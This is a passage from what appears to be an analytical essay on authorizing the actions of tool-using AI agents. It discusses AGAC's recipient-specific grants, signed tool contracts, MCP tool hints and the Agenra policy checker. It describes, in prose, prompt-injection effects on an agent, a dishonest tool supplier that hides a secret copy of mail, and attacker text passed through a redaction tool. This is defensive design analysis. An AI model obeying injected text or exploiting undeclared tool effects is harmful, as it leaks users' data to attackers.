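AgentBound's sandbox offered the same kind of guarantee, but it treated a payment to a friend and a payment to an attacker the same way. AGAC includes the recipient in the effect, so a grant can cover the payment to the friend without covering the one to the attacker.

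Hostile text can still influence what happens inside $C$. It might make the agent stop before sending anything, or send Alice the summary five times if no budget prevents this. It might also make the agent report the wrong total, since the grant specifies the summary but not its contents.

### Who vouches for the contracts

The second step of the proof depends on complete contracts. Wei and Xiong admit that for outside services, whose code nobody else can inspect, people will have to assemble contracts from developers' descriptions, program analysis and observed behaviour. If a contract omits an effect, the checker allows that effect without warning.

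Wei and Xiong allow only a service's operator, or an auditor the operator has authorized, to sign its contracts. The supplier of the hostile mail tool could therefore sign a contract that lists delivery to Priya and omits the secret copy. Wei and Xiong assume that signers are honest, so their proof doesn't cover this supplier. They rely on someone detecting the violation and revoking the contract, but the supplier would already have the mail by then.

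The signing rules do help against some other problems. A contract applies to one version of a service, so an honest update needs a new contract before agents can use it. Signers also have to publish every contract in a public log, which makes it hard to show different contracts to different users. But the checker relies on the version number the service reports, so a dishonest supplier can change the code and keep the number. Somebody who steals a signer's key can also forge contracts until the operator revokes the key.

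*Description-Code Inconsistency in Real-world MCP Servers* (2026) recommends that developers disclose any data their tools send elsewhere, and that clients consider disabling tools that don't behave as declared. These measures would catch careless developers more easily than dishonest ones.

The proof also requires every effect to pass through a checker. A service that acts without one can bypass authorization, as Wei and Xiong acknowledge. *Runtime Authorization of Self-Generated Subgoals in Long-Horizon Tool-Using AI Agents* (2026) likewise covers only effects that go through its checkpoint.

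### Calls that have no contract today

MCP's closest equivalent is four optional yes-or-no hints that a server can use to indicate whether a tool only reads, whether its changes are destructive, whether repeating a call is safe, and whether the tool deals with the outside world. None of them identifies a recipient, so emails to Alice and Bob would have identical hints.

Many tools lack even these hints. *When Tool Calls Succeed but Workflows Fail* (Trofimov and Novikov, 2026) collected the entries for 98,291 tools on remote servers in MCP's official registry and found that 26% had no hints. One publisher supplied 45% of the tools and filled in every hint for each. Among the rest, 47% had none.

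The Model Context Protocol project (2026) warns that a server can claim that a tool is read-only and then have it delete files, so clients must treat hints from untrusted servers as untrusted. The project considers a proposed hint a contract if it is useful only when true, and says that contracts belong in software that can enforce them.

Shell commands are harder to describe. The effects of `python3 setup.py` depend on code that the agent may have just written. Without a sandbox, a safe contract would have to list nearly everything the user can do on the computer. AGAC would refuse the command unless the grant were equally broad, and such a grant would protect very little. A sandbox with one folder and no network would allow a short contract, because the sandbox would limit the effects whatever the code did.

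The effect of a screen tap is also hard to describe, because it depends on what the app is showing. *Rethinking Access Control for AI Agents* describes systems that predict how an app's state will change, or that link an action such as a purchase to the web requests behind it. These systems depend on someone having already described the app or website.

A tool's developer can easily describe it. According to *Small agents should know what their tools do* (2026), the description needs only one category of effect, one yes-or-no flag and a pattern for what the tool reads and writes. But the paper's tools belong to a simulated world, where nobody has a reason to lie about them. Most designs assume that contracts exist, while *Contract2Tool* (2026) tries to learn them from observable evidence about tools. A learned contract may still miss an effect that nobody has observed, such as a copy that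 the tool sends only on Fridays.

### A smaller system that runs

Wei and Xiong report no measurements of AGAC in operation. They propose a benchmark whose first task is the copy for Bob, and acknowledge that the ledger and the contract registry might make agents too expensive for ordinary use.

*Agenra* (Shivakumar, Priya and Gao, 2026) describes a related system, which exists as working software. It has a policy language in which tools declare their effects, and a program checks each call before the tool runs. In the paper's main example, an agent may send the public parts of a private report to Alice once. The permission refers to whatever address a designated directory returns for her, so another document can't supply a different one. If the directory is right, this deals with the choice that Wei and Xiong's formula leaves unchecked.

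Agenra rejected the unedited report and a second email. It also counts failed attempts, so if the mail server is down during the attempt to send the report, Alice doesn't get it during that task.

The tests also show that Agenra depends on accurate declarations and well-designed policies. When the researchers left deletion out of a tool's declared effects, Agenra allowed the tool to delete data. Their original policy for the report also let the agent send Alice unrelated public text, because it checked only that the text was public. They added a rule that the text must come from the tool that removes private fields. An agent could still run an attacker's text through that tool and send the result, and preventing that required another rule.

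Even broadening a permission can break a task. Suppose an agent may delete file B once under its first permission and file A once under its second. If someone extends the first permission to cover either file, deleting A uses up that permission, because Agenra uses the first one that fits. The agent can then no longer delete B, but it can delete A twice. Shivakumar and colleagues built a checker for such changes. It approved all 21 of their test revisions that kept every workflow intact, and none of the 30 that broke one.

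### Why Android could manage without contracts

Android permissions also rest on known consequences, but those consequences are easier to establish on Android. For example, Google defines the location permission and writes the service that checks it and supplies the location, so nobody has to trust an outside developer's account of what reading the location does. A tool for an agent may come from any of thousands of suppliers, and its most important effects often happen on a computer that the user never sees.

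Android's permissions usually don't name a recipient either. A URI grant comes much closer to an effect in Wei and Xiong's sense, because it lets one app read one photo. Android can enforce the grant without a contract because it controls access to the photo, though it doesn't control what the app does with it afterwards.

Under AGAC, a standing grant could cover reading and reversible changes, but disclosures, payments and physical actions would need fresh human approval. Sending the expense summary to Alice is a disclosure, so an office assistant would ask for approval often. People would probably find "Send the expense summary to Alice" easier to judge than a permission to send mail. But Wei and Xiong cite Felt and colleagues' study, which found that people understood Android's warnings poorly, and leave open whether they would understand lists of effects any better.
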